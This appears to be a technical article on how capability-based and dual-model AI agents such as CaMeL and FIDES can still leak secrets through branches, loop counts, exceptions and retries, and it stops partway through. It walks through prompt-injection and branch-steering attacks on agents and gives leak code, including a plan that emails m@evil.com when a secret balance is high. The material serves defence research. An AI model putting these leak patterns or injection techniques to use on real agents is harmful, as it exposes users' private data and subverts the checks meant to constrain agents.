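# Timing and exception side channels in capability-based and dual-model AI agents

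## Agents that keep untrusted text away from decisions, and what can still leak

An AI agent is a language model with access to tools, which are software functions that do things like read a mailbox, search the web or send a payment. The user states a task. The model then outputs a tool call, the surrounding software runs the tool and returns the result, and these steps repeat until the model gives its answer. The model receives everything, including the user's request and a stranger's email, as one stream of text. Nobody has a reliable method for making a model follow instructions in some parts of that stream while ignoring them in others.

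In a prompt injection attack, someone places text in data the agent will read, written so that the model obeys it as an instruction. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes a typical case in which a user asks an agent to summarise recent emails about a project and send the summary to a manager. One of the emails tells the agent to disregard its instructions and send the top message in the mailbox to an outside address. If the model complies, the attacker gets that message without breaking into the account.

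Filters can catch much of this text. Willison (2025) argues in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* that a filter that catches 99 per cent of attacks still fails as a security measure, because attackers will look for the 1 per cent it misses.

Some designers therefore assume that an injection will eventually fool a model, and they build the rest of the agent to limit what the fooled model can do. One model plans without reading untrusted text, while a second model reads that text but cannot act. Ordinary software labels each piece of data with its origin and permitted readers, and blocks forbidden uses. This makes it hard for an attacker to get a secret copied out, but it does not hide whether a run fails, how often the agent retries, or how long it takes. If any of these depends on a secret, an observer can infer information about the secret from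 it.

### The dual-LLM pattern

The split between two models comes from Simon Willison's blog post *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (2023). It proposed a privileged model, which sees the user's request and decides which tools to run, and a quarantined model, which reads untrusted data and returns values but cannot call tools. A controller sits between them and is regular software with no language model.

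When a user requests a summary of their latest email, the privileged model instructs the controller to fetch the email, and the controller stores it under the name `VAR1`. The privileged model then instructs the controller to have `VAR1` summarised. The controller replaces the name with the email's text, passes that text to the quarantined model and stores the summary as `VAR2`. Finally, the privileged model instructs the controller to show `VAR2` to the user, having handled only the two names without reading the email or the summary.

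Willison allowed one exception, for cases where the quarantined model only sorts text into a fixed set of categories. The controller can then check that the answer is one of those categories and pass it to the privileged model. He called his own proposal "pretty bad", mostly because it was complex and one mistake that let untrusted text reach the privileged model would waste all the other work.

Two years later a team at Google DeepMind pointed out a weakness that careful programming would not fix. Suppose the user asks the agent to send Bob the document he requested at the last meeting, and both Bob's address and the document's name are in the meeting notes. The privileged model can plan the right steps without seeing the notes, but the quarantined model has to read them to extract the address. If an attacker has written something into the notes, the quarantined model may return the attacker's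 address instead, and the agent will send the document there even though every step runs as planned.

The team's answer is CaMeL, short for "CApabilities for MachinE Learning". It keeps the two models, turns the plan into a program, and adds checks on the data that passes through it.

### One email task, from request to tool call

Willison explains CaMeL with a request to find Bob's address in the user's last email and send him a reminder about tomorrow's meeting. The privileged model works from that request, without the email, and writes a short program in a restricted form of Python. The program is the plan, and it might look like this:

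```
msg  = read_latest_email()
addr = ask_quarantined("Which address belongs to Bob?", msg, type=EmailAddress)
send_email(to=addr, subject="Tomorrow", body="A reminder that we meet tomorrow.")
```

An interpreter, again ordinary software, runs the plan and labels each value with where it came from and who may read it. (CaMeL calls these labels capabilities, hence the acronym.) When the first line returns the email, the interpreter labels `msg` as text from outside. On the second line, the quarantined model reads `msg` and returns `addr`, a value in the form of an email address. Because `addr` came from `msg`, it inherits the label.

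Before the third line runs, the interpreter runs a policy check to see whether the labels of the arguments permit the call. In Willison's example, the agent may send email only to a trusted recipient. The address traces back to an email that anyone could have written, so unless it is already trusted under the user's policies, the agent asks the user to approve the message before making the tool call.

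Suppose the email contained an instruction to delete the mailbox. The quarantined model might well obey, but it has no tools, and the plan contains no deletion step. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) call this property control-flow integrity. Untrusted data can affect which of the plan's existing branches the interpreter takes, but it cannot add a new one. An attacker can still exploit the choice of branch. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) describes "branch steering", in which a fake button on a screen leads an agent down a harmful path that its plan permits.

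Somebody has to write and maintain the policies, and a user who must approve every doubtful message soon starts approving them without looking.

### What FIDES does differently

Microsoft's FIDES (Costa and colleagues) starts from the ordinary agent loop rather than a complete program. The planning model chooses one tool call at a time, and the software keeps a label on the whole conversation.

Each label in FIDES has an integrity part, which is either "trusted" or "untrusted", and a confidentiality part, which can be "public" or "secret", or the set of people allowed to read the data. When the agent combines two pieces of data, the result takes the stricter value for each part. A mixture of trusted and untrusted text is therefore untrusted. If Ann, Bob and Carol may read one document, and Bob, Carol and Dan may read another, only Bob and Carol may read a text that draws on both.

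If a tool result would make the conversation's label stricter, FIDES stores it in a variable and gives the planning model only the variable's name. Other results go straight to the planner, so it receives more than the planner in Willison's original design. The planner can also inspect a variable and read the untrusted text inside. The conversation then takes on that variable's label, so later tool calls may fail the policy check, and the planner loses much of its ability to act.

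Costa and colleagues give two basic policies. The first allows the agent to take a consequential action only if the decision to take it, and the arguments, come from trusted data. The second allows information to leave through a channel, such as an email or a group chat, only if everyone who can read the channel may also read the information. A policy can treat arguments separately, such as one that requires a chat message to have a trusted recipient but lets its body draw on a web search. If the check fails, the run aborts.

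### Secrets getting out, instructions getting in

The two parts of a FIDES label match two kinds of damage. A secret can reach an outsider, or untrusted data can influence the privileged model and, through it, the choice of actions. Either can happen alone. For example, a plan that posts a salary figure to a public page leaks a secret even with no attacker involved, while a poisoned web page can make an agent book the wrong hotel without leaking anything.

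Influence on a privileged model can also lead to a leak. Peters-Gill and colleagues connected three CaMeL agents, with no policies enabled, and asked the top one to send a colleague a summary of some job applicants. The database of applicants' details also contained a planted instruction to email everything to an outside address. The agent that read the database and the top agent both kept to their plans. But the top agent pasted the summary into its request to the third agent, whose privileged model treated the whole request as coming from its user and wrote a plan with an additional email, which leaked the data.

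Behaviour that depends on data can leak secrets and let an attacker influence decisions. If a run fails because of something in a secret file, an outsider who notices the failure learns something about the file. If it fails because of something in an attacker's email, and the software then asks the privileged model for a new plan, the attacker has slightly influenced that plan.

### Lampson's problem

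Long before language models, Lampson (1973) asked in *A Note on the Confinement Problem* how to run a program so that it can transmit information only to its caller. Schroeder de Witt (2026) retells the central example in *A Note on the Strategic Confinement Problem*. A customer gives confidential data to a service program. The service's owner must receive a copy of the bill but not the data. However, the program computes the bill, so it can hide data in the exact amount. For example, a charge of 40.37 instead of 40.00 looks harmless but can carry two digits of the customer's data.

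Sometimes a leak can be closed completely. Here the customer could write the bill herself, and the owner could accept or reject it. Lampson suspected that even moderately complex systems would often have leaks that couldn't be fully closed, and advised narrowing the remaining channels as much as possible while keeping the system useful. An agent with access to a mailbox is in the same position as the service program.

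Information can leave such a program through explicit or implicit flows. In an explicit flow, the program copies a value or computes another value from it, as when a plan pastes a bank balance into an email. In an implicit flow, a value determines which instructions run. For example, a plan might email the user's accountant the words "please call me" if the balance exceeds 10,000. The message contains no figure, but an accountant who knows the plan can infer from its arrival that the balance is above 10,000. The interpreter can label data in explicit flows fairly easily because it does the copying itself. Implicit flows are harder to track, and the guarantee that Costa and colleagues offer for FIDES deliberately excludes them.

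A side channel is any path by which observable behaviour reveals information even though the program passes no data openly. It becomes a covert channel when a sender uses it on purpose. An exception channel reveals information through an error, a refusal or a stop. A timing channel reveals it through the duration or the moment of an event. Shmatikov's lecture slides, *0x1A Great Papers in Computer Security*, define timing channels as transmitting by when something happens "(rather than what)". In a standard example, a program computes hard for a fixed interval to send a 1 and sleeps for the same interval to send a 0, while an accomplice on the same machine watches the load.

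Noninterference would rule out all of these leaks. It means that changing the protected inputs changes nothing an observer can see. For example, if an agent runs twice with the same request and public data but different bank balances, the observer must be unable to tell the runs apart, whatever the two balances are. Because a language model's answers are partly random, the test has to compare the probabilities of what the observer might see rather than two single runs.

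Full noninterference is rare in practice. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026), which models these agents as programs in a small formal language, notes that almost all guarantees of this kind are termination-insensitive, meaning that they let a protected input affect whether a run finishes, but nothing else. The strength of a guarantee also depends on what its definition assumes an observer can see. The model behind FIDES leaves out timing and the length of network packets, so an agent could meet its stated guarantee and still leak a secret to someone who times it.

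### Who sends and who watches

The sender of a leak need not be malicious. The privileged model may write a legitimate plan whose behaviour happens to depend on a secret, like the plan that emails the accountant. Such a leak is unintended and reveals only information that the task uses.

The quarantined model becomes a more dangerous source of leaks once it obeys an injection. Willison (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, recommends assuming that an attacker who gets text into a model controls all its subsequent output. The quarantined model still cannot call tools, but it can choose which permitted value to return, return malformed output so that the next step fails, or write a longer answer than necessary. It can leak a secret in these ways only if the secret is in its input. It has nothing to leak if the plan passes it only a single email from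 a stranger, but passing it the whole mailbox puts private messages in the same input as the injection.

The possible observers differ in what they can watch:

| Observer | What the observer can watch |
|---|---|
| Operator of a tool | Which calls arrive, with which arguments, in what order and when |
| Network eavesdropper | Size, direction and timing of packets, even encrypted ones |
| Retry loop | Whether a run failed, and any error text the software passes on |
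| Another customer of the model server | How quickly his own requests run while they share the machine with the agent's |

Costa and colleagues consider an attacker who resembles the tool operator. The attacker can tamper with data that tools fetch from untrusted sources and can see the effects of some tool calls, but cannot read the agent's exchanges with its model. The visible effects can be as slight as a web search showing up in a site's visitor statistics.

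The retry loop is the part of the agent that prompts the privileged model for a new plan after a run fails. In CaMeL, it sits outside the interpreter, where data carries no labels. Garby and colleagues show that an attacker can use the loop to repeat a one-bit leak until they have the whole secret.

### Counting what a run can reveal

For any of these leaks, an observer who can distinguish N outcomes of a run learns at most log₂ N bits about the secret. Randomness in the model's behaviour does not raise this limit.

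In the bank balance example, the accountant sees either a message or silence, so N = 2 and the leak is at most one bit. If the message comes at once for some balances and a minute later for others, he can distinguish three outcomes, and the limit rises to log₂ 3, about 1.58 bits. N must count every outcome the observer can tell apart, including delays and failures, so a designer who counts only tool calls will underestimate the limit.

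The limit over k runs is k times as large. A four-digit PIN has 10,000 possible values, or about 13.3 bits, so fourteen runs that leak one bit each are enough to recover it, provided each run reveals the answer to a new yes-or-no question about the PIN.

Counting bits also limits how much an attacker can influence the planner. If the quarantined model may answer only yes or no, an attacker who controls it can pass at most one bit to the planner, and Costa and colleagues let a policy accept such an answer even in a consequential action. Garby and colleagues apply the same rule to an email sorter with n possible tags, which gives an attacker at most log₂ n bits of influence. Neither figure limits how much of a secret can leak out. The attacker's possible influence also grows quickly when the format allows longer answers. Willison doubts a proposal to let through method names of up to 30 characters,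 since an attacker might write an instruction as a method name. Thirty letters, digits and underscores can carry roughly 180 bits, which is enough for a readable command.

Bits are a poor measure of harm, though. Schroeder de Witt argues that a sender who chooses what to reveal can use a tiny channel to leak the single most damaging fact, such as whether a person has a particular diagnosis. By his reasoning, a limit on leakage protects against such a sender only if it is below the information content of that fact. For a diagnosis that one person in a hundred has, that is about 0.08 bits on average, so a one-bit channel is far too wide. His note is theoretical, with no experiments, and it assumes that the sender and receiver share some idea of which fact to send. The author of an injection can easily arrange this by writing into the text which question to answer and how to signal the reply,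 whereas an honest plan has nobody arranging it. Schroeder de Witt accepts that narrowing the channel still works as Lampson intended when the harm lies in the bulk of the data, as with the full text of a mailbox.

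## Leaks through branches, loops and the order of tool calls

An interpreter that labels only copied and computed values would miss the email to the accountant. In a plan, it looks like this:

```
if balance > 10000:
    send_email(to=accountant, body="Please call me.")
```

The balance is secret, but the address comes from the user's request and the privileged model wrote the message before the run began. Both arguments are therefore public, and a policy check on them passes.

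### A label for the program's position

The usual remedy is to keep one more label for the program's current position, called the program-counter label after the part of a processor that holds the address of the next instruction. The label starts out public. The interpreter raises it to secret when it reaches a condition that depends on secret data, and lowers it again when the branch ends. Every value the program writes and every tool call it makes within the branch takes on this label as well as its own. The email above then counts as secret, despite its bland text, and the policy check blocks it unless the accountant is allowed to read the balance.

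CaMeL's interpreter keeps such a label, according to Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*. They consider a plan that emails "rich!" to an attacker if the customer's balance exceeds a threshold, and report that CaMeL refuses the call. (The refusal can itself be informative, like any other failed run.)

### The assignment that never runs

A branch can also change a variable, and the plan can act on that variable later. CaMeL raises a variable's label when it carries out an assignment under a secret condition. If the condition is false, it carries out no assignment and raises no label. Garby and colleagues exploit this gap with a plan along these lines:

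```
rich = True
tmp  = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

| Line | Balance above the threshold | Balance at or below the threshold |
|---|---|---|
| `rich = True`, `tmp = True` | Both are True and public | Both are True and public |
| `if balance > threshold: tmp = False` | Assignment runs; `tmp` is False and secret | Assignment does not run; `tmp` is still True and public |
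| `if tmp: rich = False` | Assignment does not run; `rich` is still True and public | Assignment runs under a public condition; `rich` is False and public |
| `if rich: send_email(...)` | The condition is public, so the email goes out | No email |

In both runs `rich` ends up labeled public, and it is True exactly when the secret balance is above the threshold. When the balance is high, the interpreter skips `rich = False`, so `rich` stays True. That value depends on the secret, but the interpreter doesn't change the label because the assignment never runs.

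A shorter plan could leak the same bit without `tmp`. It would set `rich` to True, then change it to False if the balance is at or below the threshold. With a high balance, that second assignment would not run, so `rich` would stay public and the email would go out. With a low balance, `rich` would become secret, but the plan would send nothing anyway. Using `tmp` is more useful to the plan because `rich` then looks public in both runs, so the interpreter would allow the plan to email its value, whether True or False.

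Each use of the trick reveals one bit without stopping the run, so a plan can repeat it many times. A whole-number balance below 16,384 can be written in 14 binary digits, so 14 copies of the code, each testing one digit, would reveal it exactly in a single run.

An attacker cannot give this code to CaMeL directly, because the privileged model writes the plan without reading untrusted data, and an uncompromised model is unlikely to write such roundabout code. The example shows a gap in the labels' guarantees more than a ready-made attack. An attacker could use it once injected text reaches a privileged model, as happened in the three-agent chain that Peters-Gill and colleagues built.

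The trick is much older than AI agents. Garby and colleagues trace it to Fenton's *Memoryless Subsystems* (1974). Denning later rewrote it as ordinary program code, and other researchers rediscovered it decades afterwards.

### Stopping the run before the label changes

Austin and Flanagan (2009) showed in *Efficient purely-dynamic information flow analysis* how to close the leak by checking only the lines that run. Under their rule, now known as no-sensitive-upgrade, code whose execution depends on secret data may not assign to a variable currently labelled public. If it tries, the interpreter stops the run.

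The plan above sends the attacker no email, whatever the balance. If the balance is high, the plan stops at `tmp = False`, before it can send anything. If the balance is low, it runs to the end but sends nothing because `rich` is False. Whether the run finishes still depends on the balance, so the guarantee is termination-insensitive.

The same problem arises with a model's conversation history, which a program can change much like a variable. In an example by Garby and colleagues, a program tells a model to remember that x is false. If a secret is true, the program then tells the model to set x to true. In either case, it finally asks the model for x. Their interpreter stops the run before the program sends the conditional message. Marking the history as secret when that message is sent would not be enough, because if the secret is false, the message is never sent, and both the history and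 the answer "false" stay public.

The rule also stops runs that leak nothing. Suppose a plan sets a public variable `urgent` to True if the balance is below 100, and then saves it in the user's private notes. No outsider sees the notes, but the interpreter still stops at the assignment. If the agent has already sent one of two emails when the run stops, a second attempt would send that email again.

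The plan's author can avoid the stop by marking `urgent` secret before the branch in every run. That takes some foresight, especially from a language model writing a new plan for each request. *Permissive dynamic information flow analysis* (Austin and Flanagan, 2010) describes how to infer where such markings belong and insert them automatically, so that more programs run to completion with the same termination-insensitive guarantee. The paper calls data like `tmp` partially leaked, because its value depends on a secret while its label may be private in one run and public in another.

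An interpreter could instead analyse the plan before running it. At the line `if balance > threshold`, it would find that one branch assigns to `tmp`, and mark `tmp` secret whether or not that branch runs. It would do the same for `rich` one line later, and then refuse to send the email. Russo and Sabelfeld, in *Dynamic vs. Static Flow-Sensitive Security Analysis*, argue that once labels can change during a run, tracking based only on the running program must either miss some leaks or stop some safe programs that an analysis done in advance would accept. CaMeL could use such an analysis because the whole plan exists before the first tool call, but FIDES has no complete plan to analyse because its planner picks one call at a time.

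### Loops that count out a secret

A branch on a secret reveals one bit, but a loop can reveal much more. Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, give this example:

```
for i in range(secret): fetch("ping")
```

A loop can leak a secret number through how many requests it sends, even if the requests are identical and contain nothing private. If the secret is the PIN 4721 and the loop sends that many requests, the server's access log will show 4,721 entries, and a single run leaks all 13.3 bits. A plan written for a legitimate task can leak information the same way by accident. If it looks up an exchange rate once for each unpaid foreign invoice, the operator of the rate service can count the invoices.

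Tallam and Miller propose stricter tracking for any loop whose length depends on a secret. Inside such a loop, the interpreter would block tool calls that change state, or ask the user to approve them. This applies the idea of the program-counter label to loops, but its effectiveness depends heavily on which calls count as changing state. A designer might well class `fetch` as a harmless read, and the leak in the example would still work. The rule would have to cover every call an outsider can see, even a web search.

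They also suggest capping the number of repetitions. A cap of ten leaves eleven possible counts, from zero to ten, so the count can leak at most about 3.5 bits. However, the plan then cannot handle an eleventh invoice.

Tallam and Miller also propose combining the repeated calls into one bulk request. This hides the count from someone who can only count requests, but not from the operator of the rate service, who can read the list of currencies in the request. A network eavesdropper may also be able to estimate the list's length from the size of the packets. To hide the count from both, the agent would have to pad the list to a fixed length and send it even when there are no invoices. Tallam and Miller say that these measures, together with others for errors and timing, can suppress the most practical side channels, but they report no tests of them.

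### What FIDES guarantees

Costa and colleagues prove that FIDES satisfies explicit secrecy. This guarantee covers only what happens to data along the path a run actually takes, and leaves out implicit flows.

Let g be the combined effect of the fixed sequence of steps a run has taken so far on the data held by the tools. Explicit secrecy requires that whenever two starting states of that data, d₁ and d₂, agree on everything public, g(d₁) and g(d₂) do too, even if d₁ and d₂ differ in their secrets.

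A step that copies the bank balance onto a public page breaks this requirement, because g would write 500 in one case and 50,000 in the other. The email to the accountant does not break it. On the path where the agent sends the email, g puts the same three words in the outbox whatever the balance is, and on the path where the agent sends nothing, g leaves the outbox unchanged. Both paths satisfy explicit secrecy, which checks each path separately, whereas noninterference compares them.

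Costa and colleagues regard noninterference as too restrictive for an agent. Software cannot tell which parts of a model's input affected its answer, so it has to assume that every decision depends on everything the model has read. Noninterference would then, they say, essentially ban any call with publicly visible effects after any call that may read a secret. An agent that had checked the user's private calendar could not then book a table through a restaurant's website. They note that web browsers and TaintDroid, a system for tracking private data on Android phones, also settle for less than noninterference in trying to stop data from being copied out.

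Garby and colleagues object that explicit secrecy is weakest where data and control are interchangeable, because leaks through control can then be efficient. This fairly describes an agent, because the text the model reads determines what it does. Their own language has a noninterference theorem and runs a working agent, so this stronger property may be practical, although their agent needs a way to declare selected untrusted data trusted.

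How much FIDES can leak this way depends on which calls an observer can see. Costa and colleagues say that someone who sees the sequence of tool calls may infer "limited information" from the agent's decisions, but the amount can still be substantial. Suppose the planner has two public web links stored in variables. It reads a secret medical file and then opens one of the links. In FIDES, an argument taken from a variable keeps that variable's label, so the link still counts as public. The basic confidentiality policy checks only the labels of the arguments, so it permits the call even though the choice of link may depend on the file. With sixteen links to choose from, each request can carry four bits, so four requests are enough to leak a four-digit PIN.

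FIDES keeps a separate label for the decision to make a call. A stricter policy could check that label and refuse any visible call the planner chose after reading a secret, but this is close to the ban that Costa and colleagues wanted to avoid.

A policy in FIDES can also release information on purpose. The labels can record the type of answer the quarantined model gave, ranked by how much information it can carry, from yes-or-no answers to choices from a fixed list to free text. A policy could let a yes-or-no answer about a secret leave the system because it reveals so little. Garby and colleagues object that nobody can tell from a particular run whether such an answer is an intended release or a real leak. They also note that Costa and colleagues left this option off in their own evaluation.

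Experiments have also found leaks through an agent's choice of actions. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) tests an attack that needs no prompt injection. In its running scenario, an assistant has access to a man's mental health diagnosis, and his former wife wants to learn it. She creates a shared page of true and false statements about him and asks the assistant to clean it up. The assistant deletes the false statements but refuses to delete the true ones, so she can tell which are true from what remains.

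The assistant writes nothing private, and every entry on the page is the attacker's own text, so software that tracked only copied data would not flag the leak. On a real agent connected to Gmail and Notion, the attack extracted 34.7 per cent of the sensitive items despite PrivacyChecker, a defence that prompts the model to look for privacy violations. Shim and colleagues reduced this to zero with a check on every write and share that runs outside the model's conversation. They showed that the channel works against an ordinary agent, but did not test how much FIDES or CaMeL would leak.

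### Steering an agent through its own plan

Branches also carry information the other way, from an attacker into the agent's decisions. Peters-Gill and colleagues define a control-flow plan as a program, fixed in advance, that determines the tool calls "as a function of intermediate tool return values". An agent has control-flow integrity if it follows such a plan, derived only from the user's request and other trusted information.

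The definition does not cover who supplies the values that tools return. If a plan contains the line "if the invoice is marked urgent, pay it today", an attacker who writes the invoice can decide whether the agent pays today. The agent still follows its plan, so it keeps its control-flow integrity. Some influence of this kind is unavoidable, because many tasks need a plan that can react to what its tools return. In the scheme of Peters-Gill and colleagues, the policy checks on each tool call have to provide the protection against a bad choice of branch.

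Garby and colleagues found an extreme case when they ran CaMeL with its policy checks off. The user had asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The privileged model couldn't see the file, so it wrote a loop that read each instruction and called the matching tool. Because the plan had a branch for every tool, whoever wrote the file could choose which tools the agent called and in what order, and two attacks succeeded this way.

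Computer-use agents, which click and type on a screen as a person would, constantly face this problem. The privileged model has to plan for cookie banners, login forms and failed clicks without seeing the pages. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, these plans had 39.7 branches on average, compared with 3.7 for plans in AgentDojo, a benchmark whose tools have clear functions such as sending an email. About half the steps in the computer-use plans were fallbacks that a given run never reached.

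At many of these branches, a quarantined model answers a yes-or-no question about the screen, such as whether a cookie banner is visible. In one attack from the same paper, an advertisement contains a fake cookie banner. When the agent follows its plan to find and click the banner, the quarantined model returns the position of the fake, and the click takes the agent to the attacker's website. A policy check on the click offers little protection, since a click at a given position might close a banner or confirm a bank transfer.

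The program-counter label would help here too, if it tracked trust as well as secrecy. When a condition depended on untrusted data, the interpreter would mark the program's position untrusted, and a policy could block any consequential call until the branch ended. But nearly everything on a web page is untrusted, so a computer-use agent under this policy could do very little.

*Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues, 2026) measured how well the attack works on a benchmark of 101 tasks, ranging from bank transfers to adjusting drug doses. Attacks succeeded 94.4 per cent of the time against an ordinary agent that reads the screen and picks each action as it goes. They succeeded 89.5 per cent of the time against an agent with separate privileged and quarantined models but no further checks. Fixing the plan in advance therefore gave almost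 no protection against an attacker who used the plan's own branches.

The COBRA defence limits which sites and tools each branch may use, and which values it may send, before the agent sees any untrusted data. Software between the agent and the network then checks the requests that the agent's clicks produce, because the requests have a clearer meaning than the clicks. If the task needs a sensitive value, such as an account number, and no trusted source can supply it, COBRA prompts the user. None of the benchmark's attacks succeeded, and on tasks without an attack, COBRA's success rate was 97 per cent of the other two-model agent's.

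Zingrillo and colleagues designed both the defence and the benchmark, and they count an attack as successful only if the harmful action breaks the limits in force at that point. Untrusted data can still determine which branch runs in COBRA, provided the resulting request stays within the limits. If the privileged model sets those limits too loosely, an attacker can steer the agent to a harmful result, and the benchmark would not count the attack as successful.

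## Leaks through exceptions, refused calls and retries

A plan that stops halfway can leak a secret without making any unusual tool call. Suppose a plan checks the user's bank balance and then looks up an exchange rate, and the first step raises an error whenever the balance is above 10,000. The exchange rate request contains nothing private and is the same in every run that reaches it. But if the operator of the rate service knows the plan, he can infer from a missing request that the balance is above 10,000.

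Tallam and Miller put this leak at one bit per execution, because an exception that occurs only when a secret meets some condition reveals whether the condition holds. One bit is often harmless, but the leak becomes serious when the software around the plan retries after each failure.

### How a run can fail

| Failure | Example | Protected data that can decide it | Who can notice |
|---|---|---|---|
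| Program error | The plan takes the first item from an empty list | Any value the plan computes with | The retry loop, and operators of tools the plan would have called next |
| Refused policy check | The plan sends a file to someone who may not read it | The labels of the arguments and of the program's position | The same observers, and the person who was due to receive the file |
| Unusable answer from the quarantined model | Asked for a date, the model returns a sentence or answers that the text contains no date | Everything in the model's input, including an injection | The retry loop, and operators of tools the plan would have called next |
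| Tool error | A bank rejects a payment because the account is short of money | Data the tool holds, and the arguments of the call | The tool's operator first, then the same observers |

A program error reveals information only when its occurrence depends on protected data. For example, a plan that looks up the first overdue bill fails in months when there isn't one. A misspelled variable name reveals nothing, because the plan fails at that line whatever the data.

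An attacker has the most direct control over failures of the quarantined model. They can email an instruction to return an answer of the wrong type, which makes the interpreter raise an error. If the model's input also includes private text, the attacker can make the failure depend on that text, for example by telling the model to return a sentence instead of a date if any message mentions a hospital.

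Tool errors also bring in text from outside. The operator of a malicious website can put an instruction in its "page not found" message, and the instruction becomes an injection if that message reaches a model.

### Refusals as signals

A policy check can block a message and still leak the fact that the message would have revealed. Take this plan, in which the outsider may not read the balance:

```
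if balance > 10000:
    send_email(to=outsider, body="Hello")
rate = get_exchange_rate("EUR")
```

If the balance is high, the plan enters the branch and the program-counter label becomes secret. The policy check then refuses the email, the run stops, and the rate service receives no request. If the balance is low, the plan skips the branch and requests the rate. The check keeps the outsider from learning about the balance through the email, but the operator of the rate service can infer whether it is high from whether a request arrives. The check therefore gives little protection if the outsider runs the rate service.

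A refusal can also leak information contained in a label, such as the list of permitted readers in FIDES. Suppose the user asks an agent to send Bob a summary of this afternoon's meeting, which only the people invited may read. The interpreter has to check the guest list before sending the summary, so if Bob knows of the request and no summary arrives, he can guess that he was not invited. If the meeting is about redundancies, the guest list may be as sensitive as the minutes.

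A language model's refusals can leak information in the same way. *Eight in Ten LLMs Leak System-Prompt Secrets* (2026) describes a model that often refused to repeat a list of short strings when the list included a fragment of a secret in its prompt, but complied when the fragment was absent.

### Exceptions in languages that track labels

Programming-language researchers encountered this problem long before it arose in AI agents. *Flexible Dynamic Information Flow Control in the Presence of Exceptions* (Stefan, Russo and colleagues, 2012) describes LIO, a library that adds label tracking to Haskell. LIO keeps one label for the whole computation and raises it as the computation reads more sensitive data. On its own, this would soon make everything secret, so a program can put the sensitive part in a block. When the block ends, LIO returns the block's result under a secret label and resets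 the computation's label to its earlier value.

An exception that jumps out of such a block can leak a secret. In a Python-like notation, the example from Stefan and colleagues looks like this:

```
flag = True
try:
    with secret_block():
        if secret: raise Error
    flag = False
except Error:
    pass
```

If the secret is True, the exception skips the line `flag = False`, so `flag` stays True. If the secret is False, the block ends normally and `flag` becomes False. Either way, `flag` ends up equal to the secret, even though the program wrote to it only while the computation's label was public.

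LIO closes this leak by making the block catch every exception raised inside it. The block always returns a labelled result containing either a value or an exception, so the line after the block always runs. The exception reappears only if the program opens the result, and opening it raises the computation's label to secret. Code that handles the exception runs under that label, so it cannot write to anything public.

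LIO also lets a program recover from a refusal. Each computation can have a clearance, an upper limit on how secret its label may become. When a program tries to open a value above its clearance, LIO compares the labels and refuses before the program has read anything. The refusal therefore depends on the value's label and reveals nothing about its content. Stefan and colleagues illustrate this with a system for reviewing conference papers. When a reviewer with a conflict of interest tries to read a review, his program catches the refusal and logs "In conflict!" In the exchange-rate example, by contrast, the refusal came after the plan had read the balance and branched on it.

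A refusal that depends only on a label is still unsafe if the label depends on a secret. In *All your IFCException are belong to us* (2013), Hrițcu, Greenberg and colleagues give an example that returns an empty value in every run, but labels it "secret" if a hidden bit is true and "top secret" if it is false. If a later check accepts secret data and refuses top-secret data, its outcome reveals the bit.

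Hrițcu and colleagues describe two consistent ways to keep labels, and the errors that arise from checking them, from leaking secrets. A system can let labels depend on secrets, but it must then hide both the labels and the errors. Or it can prevent labels from depending on secrets, which lets programs freely inspect both. They chose the second approach, in which the programmer declares the label of a block's result in advance.

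The leak can occur only if there are at least two labels that an outsider cannot read. With only "public" and "secret", everything hidden has the same label, so a check on labels cannot distinguish between hidden values. Garby and colleagues note that the label test in Austin and Flanagan's early design is sound only in this two-label case. FIDES can have a separate label for every set of readers, so a designer cannot assume its refusals are harmless.

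When an exception jumps out of a block, Hrițcu and colleagues also convert the error into a labelled result. Their more radical design has no ordinary exceptions. A failed operation produces a "not-a-value", which the program stores and passes on like any other value. It carries a label, an error message, the place where the error arose and the route it took through the program. They proved termination-insensitive noninterference even with this detail included, so detailed error reports are compatible with secrecy as long as the labels stay attached. However, existing programs would not run unchanged under this design.

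Labelled exceptions are also easy to get wrong. According to *IFC Inside* (2015), LIO's original treatment of exceptions handled clearance incorrectly. It also always passed errors such as division by zero up to trusted code, which untrusted programs could exploit to disrupt that code. LIO later adopted a simpler design.

### How the retry loop loses the label

In CaMeL, an error passes from the interpreter to the retry loop, where data carries no labels. When a plan fails because of a secret, the loop works as follows:

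1. The privileged model writes a plan from the user's request, and the interpreter starts running it with the program's position labelled public.
2. The plan reads the secret and branches on it, and the interpreter raises the position's label to secret.
3. The plan fails inside the branch, and the interpreter stops and reports an error to the loop.
4. The loop adds a description of the failure to the privileged model's conversation and asks for a new plan. The secret label does not go with it.
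5. The interpreter runs the new plan, again starting from a public position.

After the fourth step, the privileged model's conversation contains one unlabeled bit about the secret. The first run could reveal this bit only through a missing call, but the model could now write it into its next plan as a constant, such as an email with the body "The balance is high." The policy check would let the email through because the interpreter treats text written by the privileged model as public.

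Each further attempt can leak another bit, until the whole secret is revealed. Garby and colleagues object that nothing in CaMeL's label tracking limits how often the leak can repeat. They do not object to the single bit, which a termination-insensitive guarantee would also allow.

A retry loop is still useful because models make mistakes when they write programs. In one example from the same paper, GPT-5.2 wrote a working factorial function in the researchers' own unfamiliar language on its third attempt, after receiving the error messages from the first two. Those errors concerned only the syntax of the model's code, so they revealed no secrets. But without labels, a loop cannot distinguish such an error from one caused by the user's bank balance.

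Keeping the label on the error would cause a different problem. Suppose an attempt fails after the agent reads an untrusted web page. If the label carried over to the privileged model's conversation, every later plan would count as untrusted, and a payment tool that requires trusted arguments would not run. Garby and colleagues encountered this problem while building their own agent and avoid it by having the agent practise on simulated tools first.

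### How much ten attempts can reveal

The figures here are illustrative because they assume a particular secret, number of attempts and set of error types. Suppose the secret is a six-digit code. It has 1,000,000 possible values, or about 19.9 bits, so 20 yes-or-no outcomes are enough to identify it.

Suppose also that the loop allows ten attempts and stops at the first success. It can succeed on any of the ten attempts or fail on all of them, which makes 11 possible outcomes, or about 3.5 bits (log₂ 11). Ten independent yes-or-no answers would give 10 bits, but here no attempts follow the first success. At 3.5 bits per user request, six requests are enough to leak the whole code, since 11⁶ is about 1.8 million and 11⁵ is only about 161,000.

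A plan designed to leak can keep the loop going by failing every time:

```
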